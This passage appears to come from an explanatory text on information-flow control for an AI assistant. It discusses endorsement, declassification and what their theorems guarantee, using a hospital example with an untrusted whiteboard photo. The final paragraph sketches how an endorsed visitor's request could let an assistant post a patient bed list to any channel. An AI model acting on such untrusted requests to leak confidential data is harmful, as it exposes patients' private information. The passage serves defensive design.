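The assistant may now run the script but still may not show it to Cam. If the program reads the whiteboard to decide whether to endorse the script, that decision depends on untrusted data, so the pc is untrusted and the script stays untrusted.

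The theorem that endorsement cannot leak confidential data is stated for an observer who ignores integrity labels, so changing those labels cannot weaken it. Each endorsement is also a visible instruction in the program, so a reviewer can find it and ask why it is there.

Garby and colleagues' construction also works with the two parts swapped, so that the operation is declassification and the guarantee protects integrity. Suppose the hospital bases its closure notice on the whiteboard photo. Declassification changes the notice's label from ⟨untrusted, {Ada, Ben}⟩ to ⟨untrusted, everyone⟩. The hospital can then publish the notice, but the notice still cannot trigger a change in the scheduling system. The theorem does not limit how much the notice reveals about patients, so the hospital still needs one of the four release rules for that.

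The theorem protects whichever part the program does not reclassify. If a hospital had to run the script and publish the notice in the same program, it would need both operations, which one use of the theorem would not cover. The two operations can also interact. If Ada endorses a visitor's message asking for the bed list, the request becomes trusted, and a policy like Microsoft's would then let the assistant post the list to any channel.
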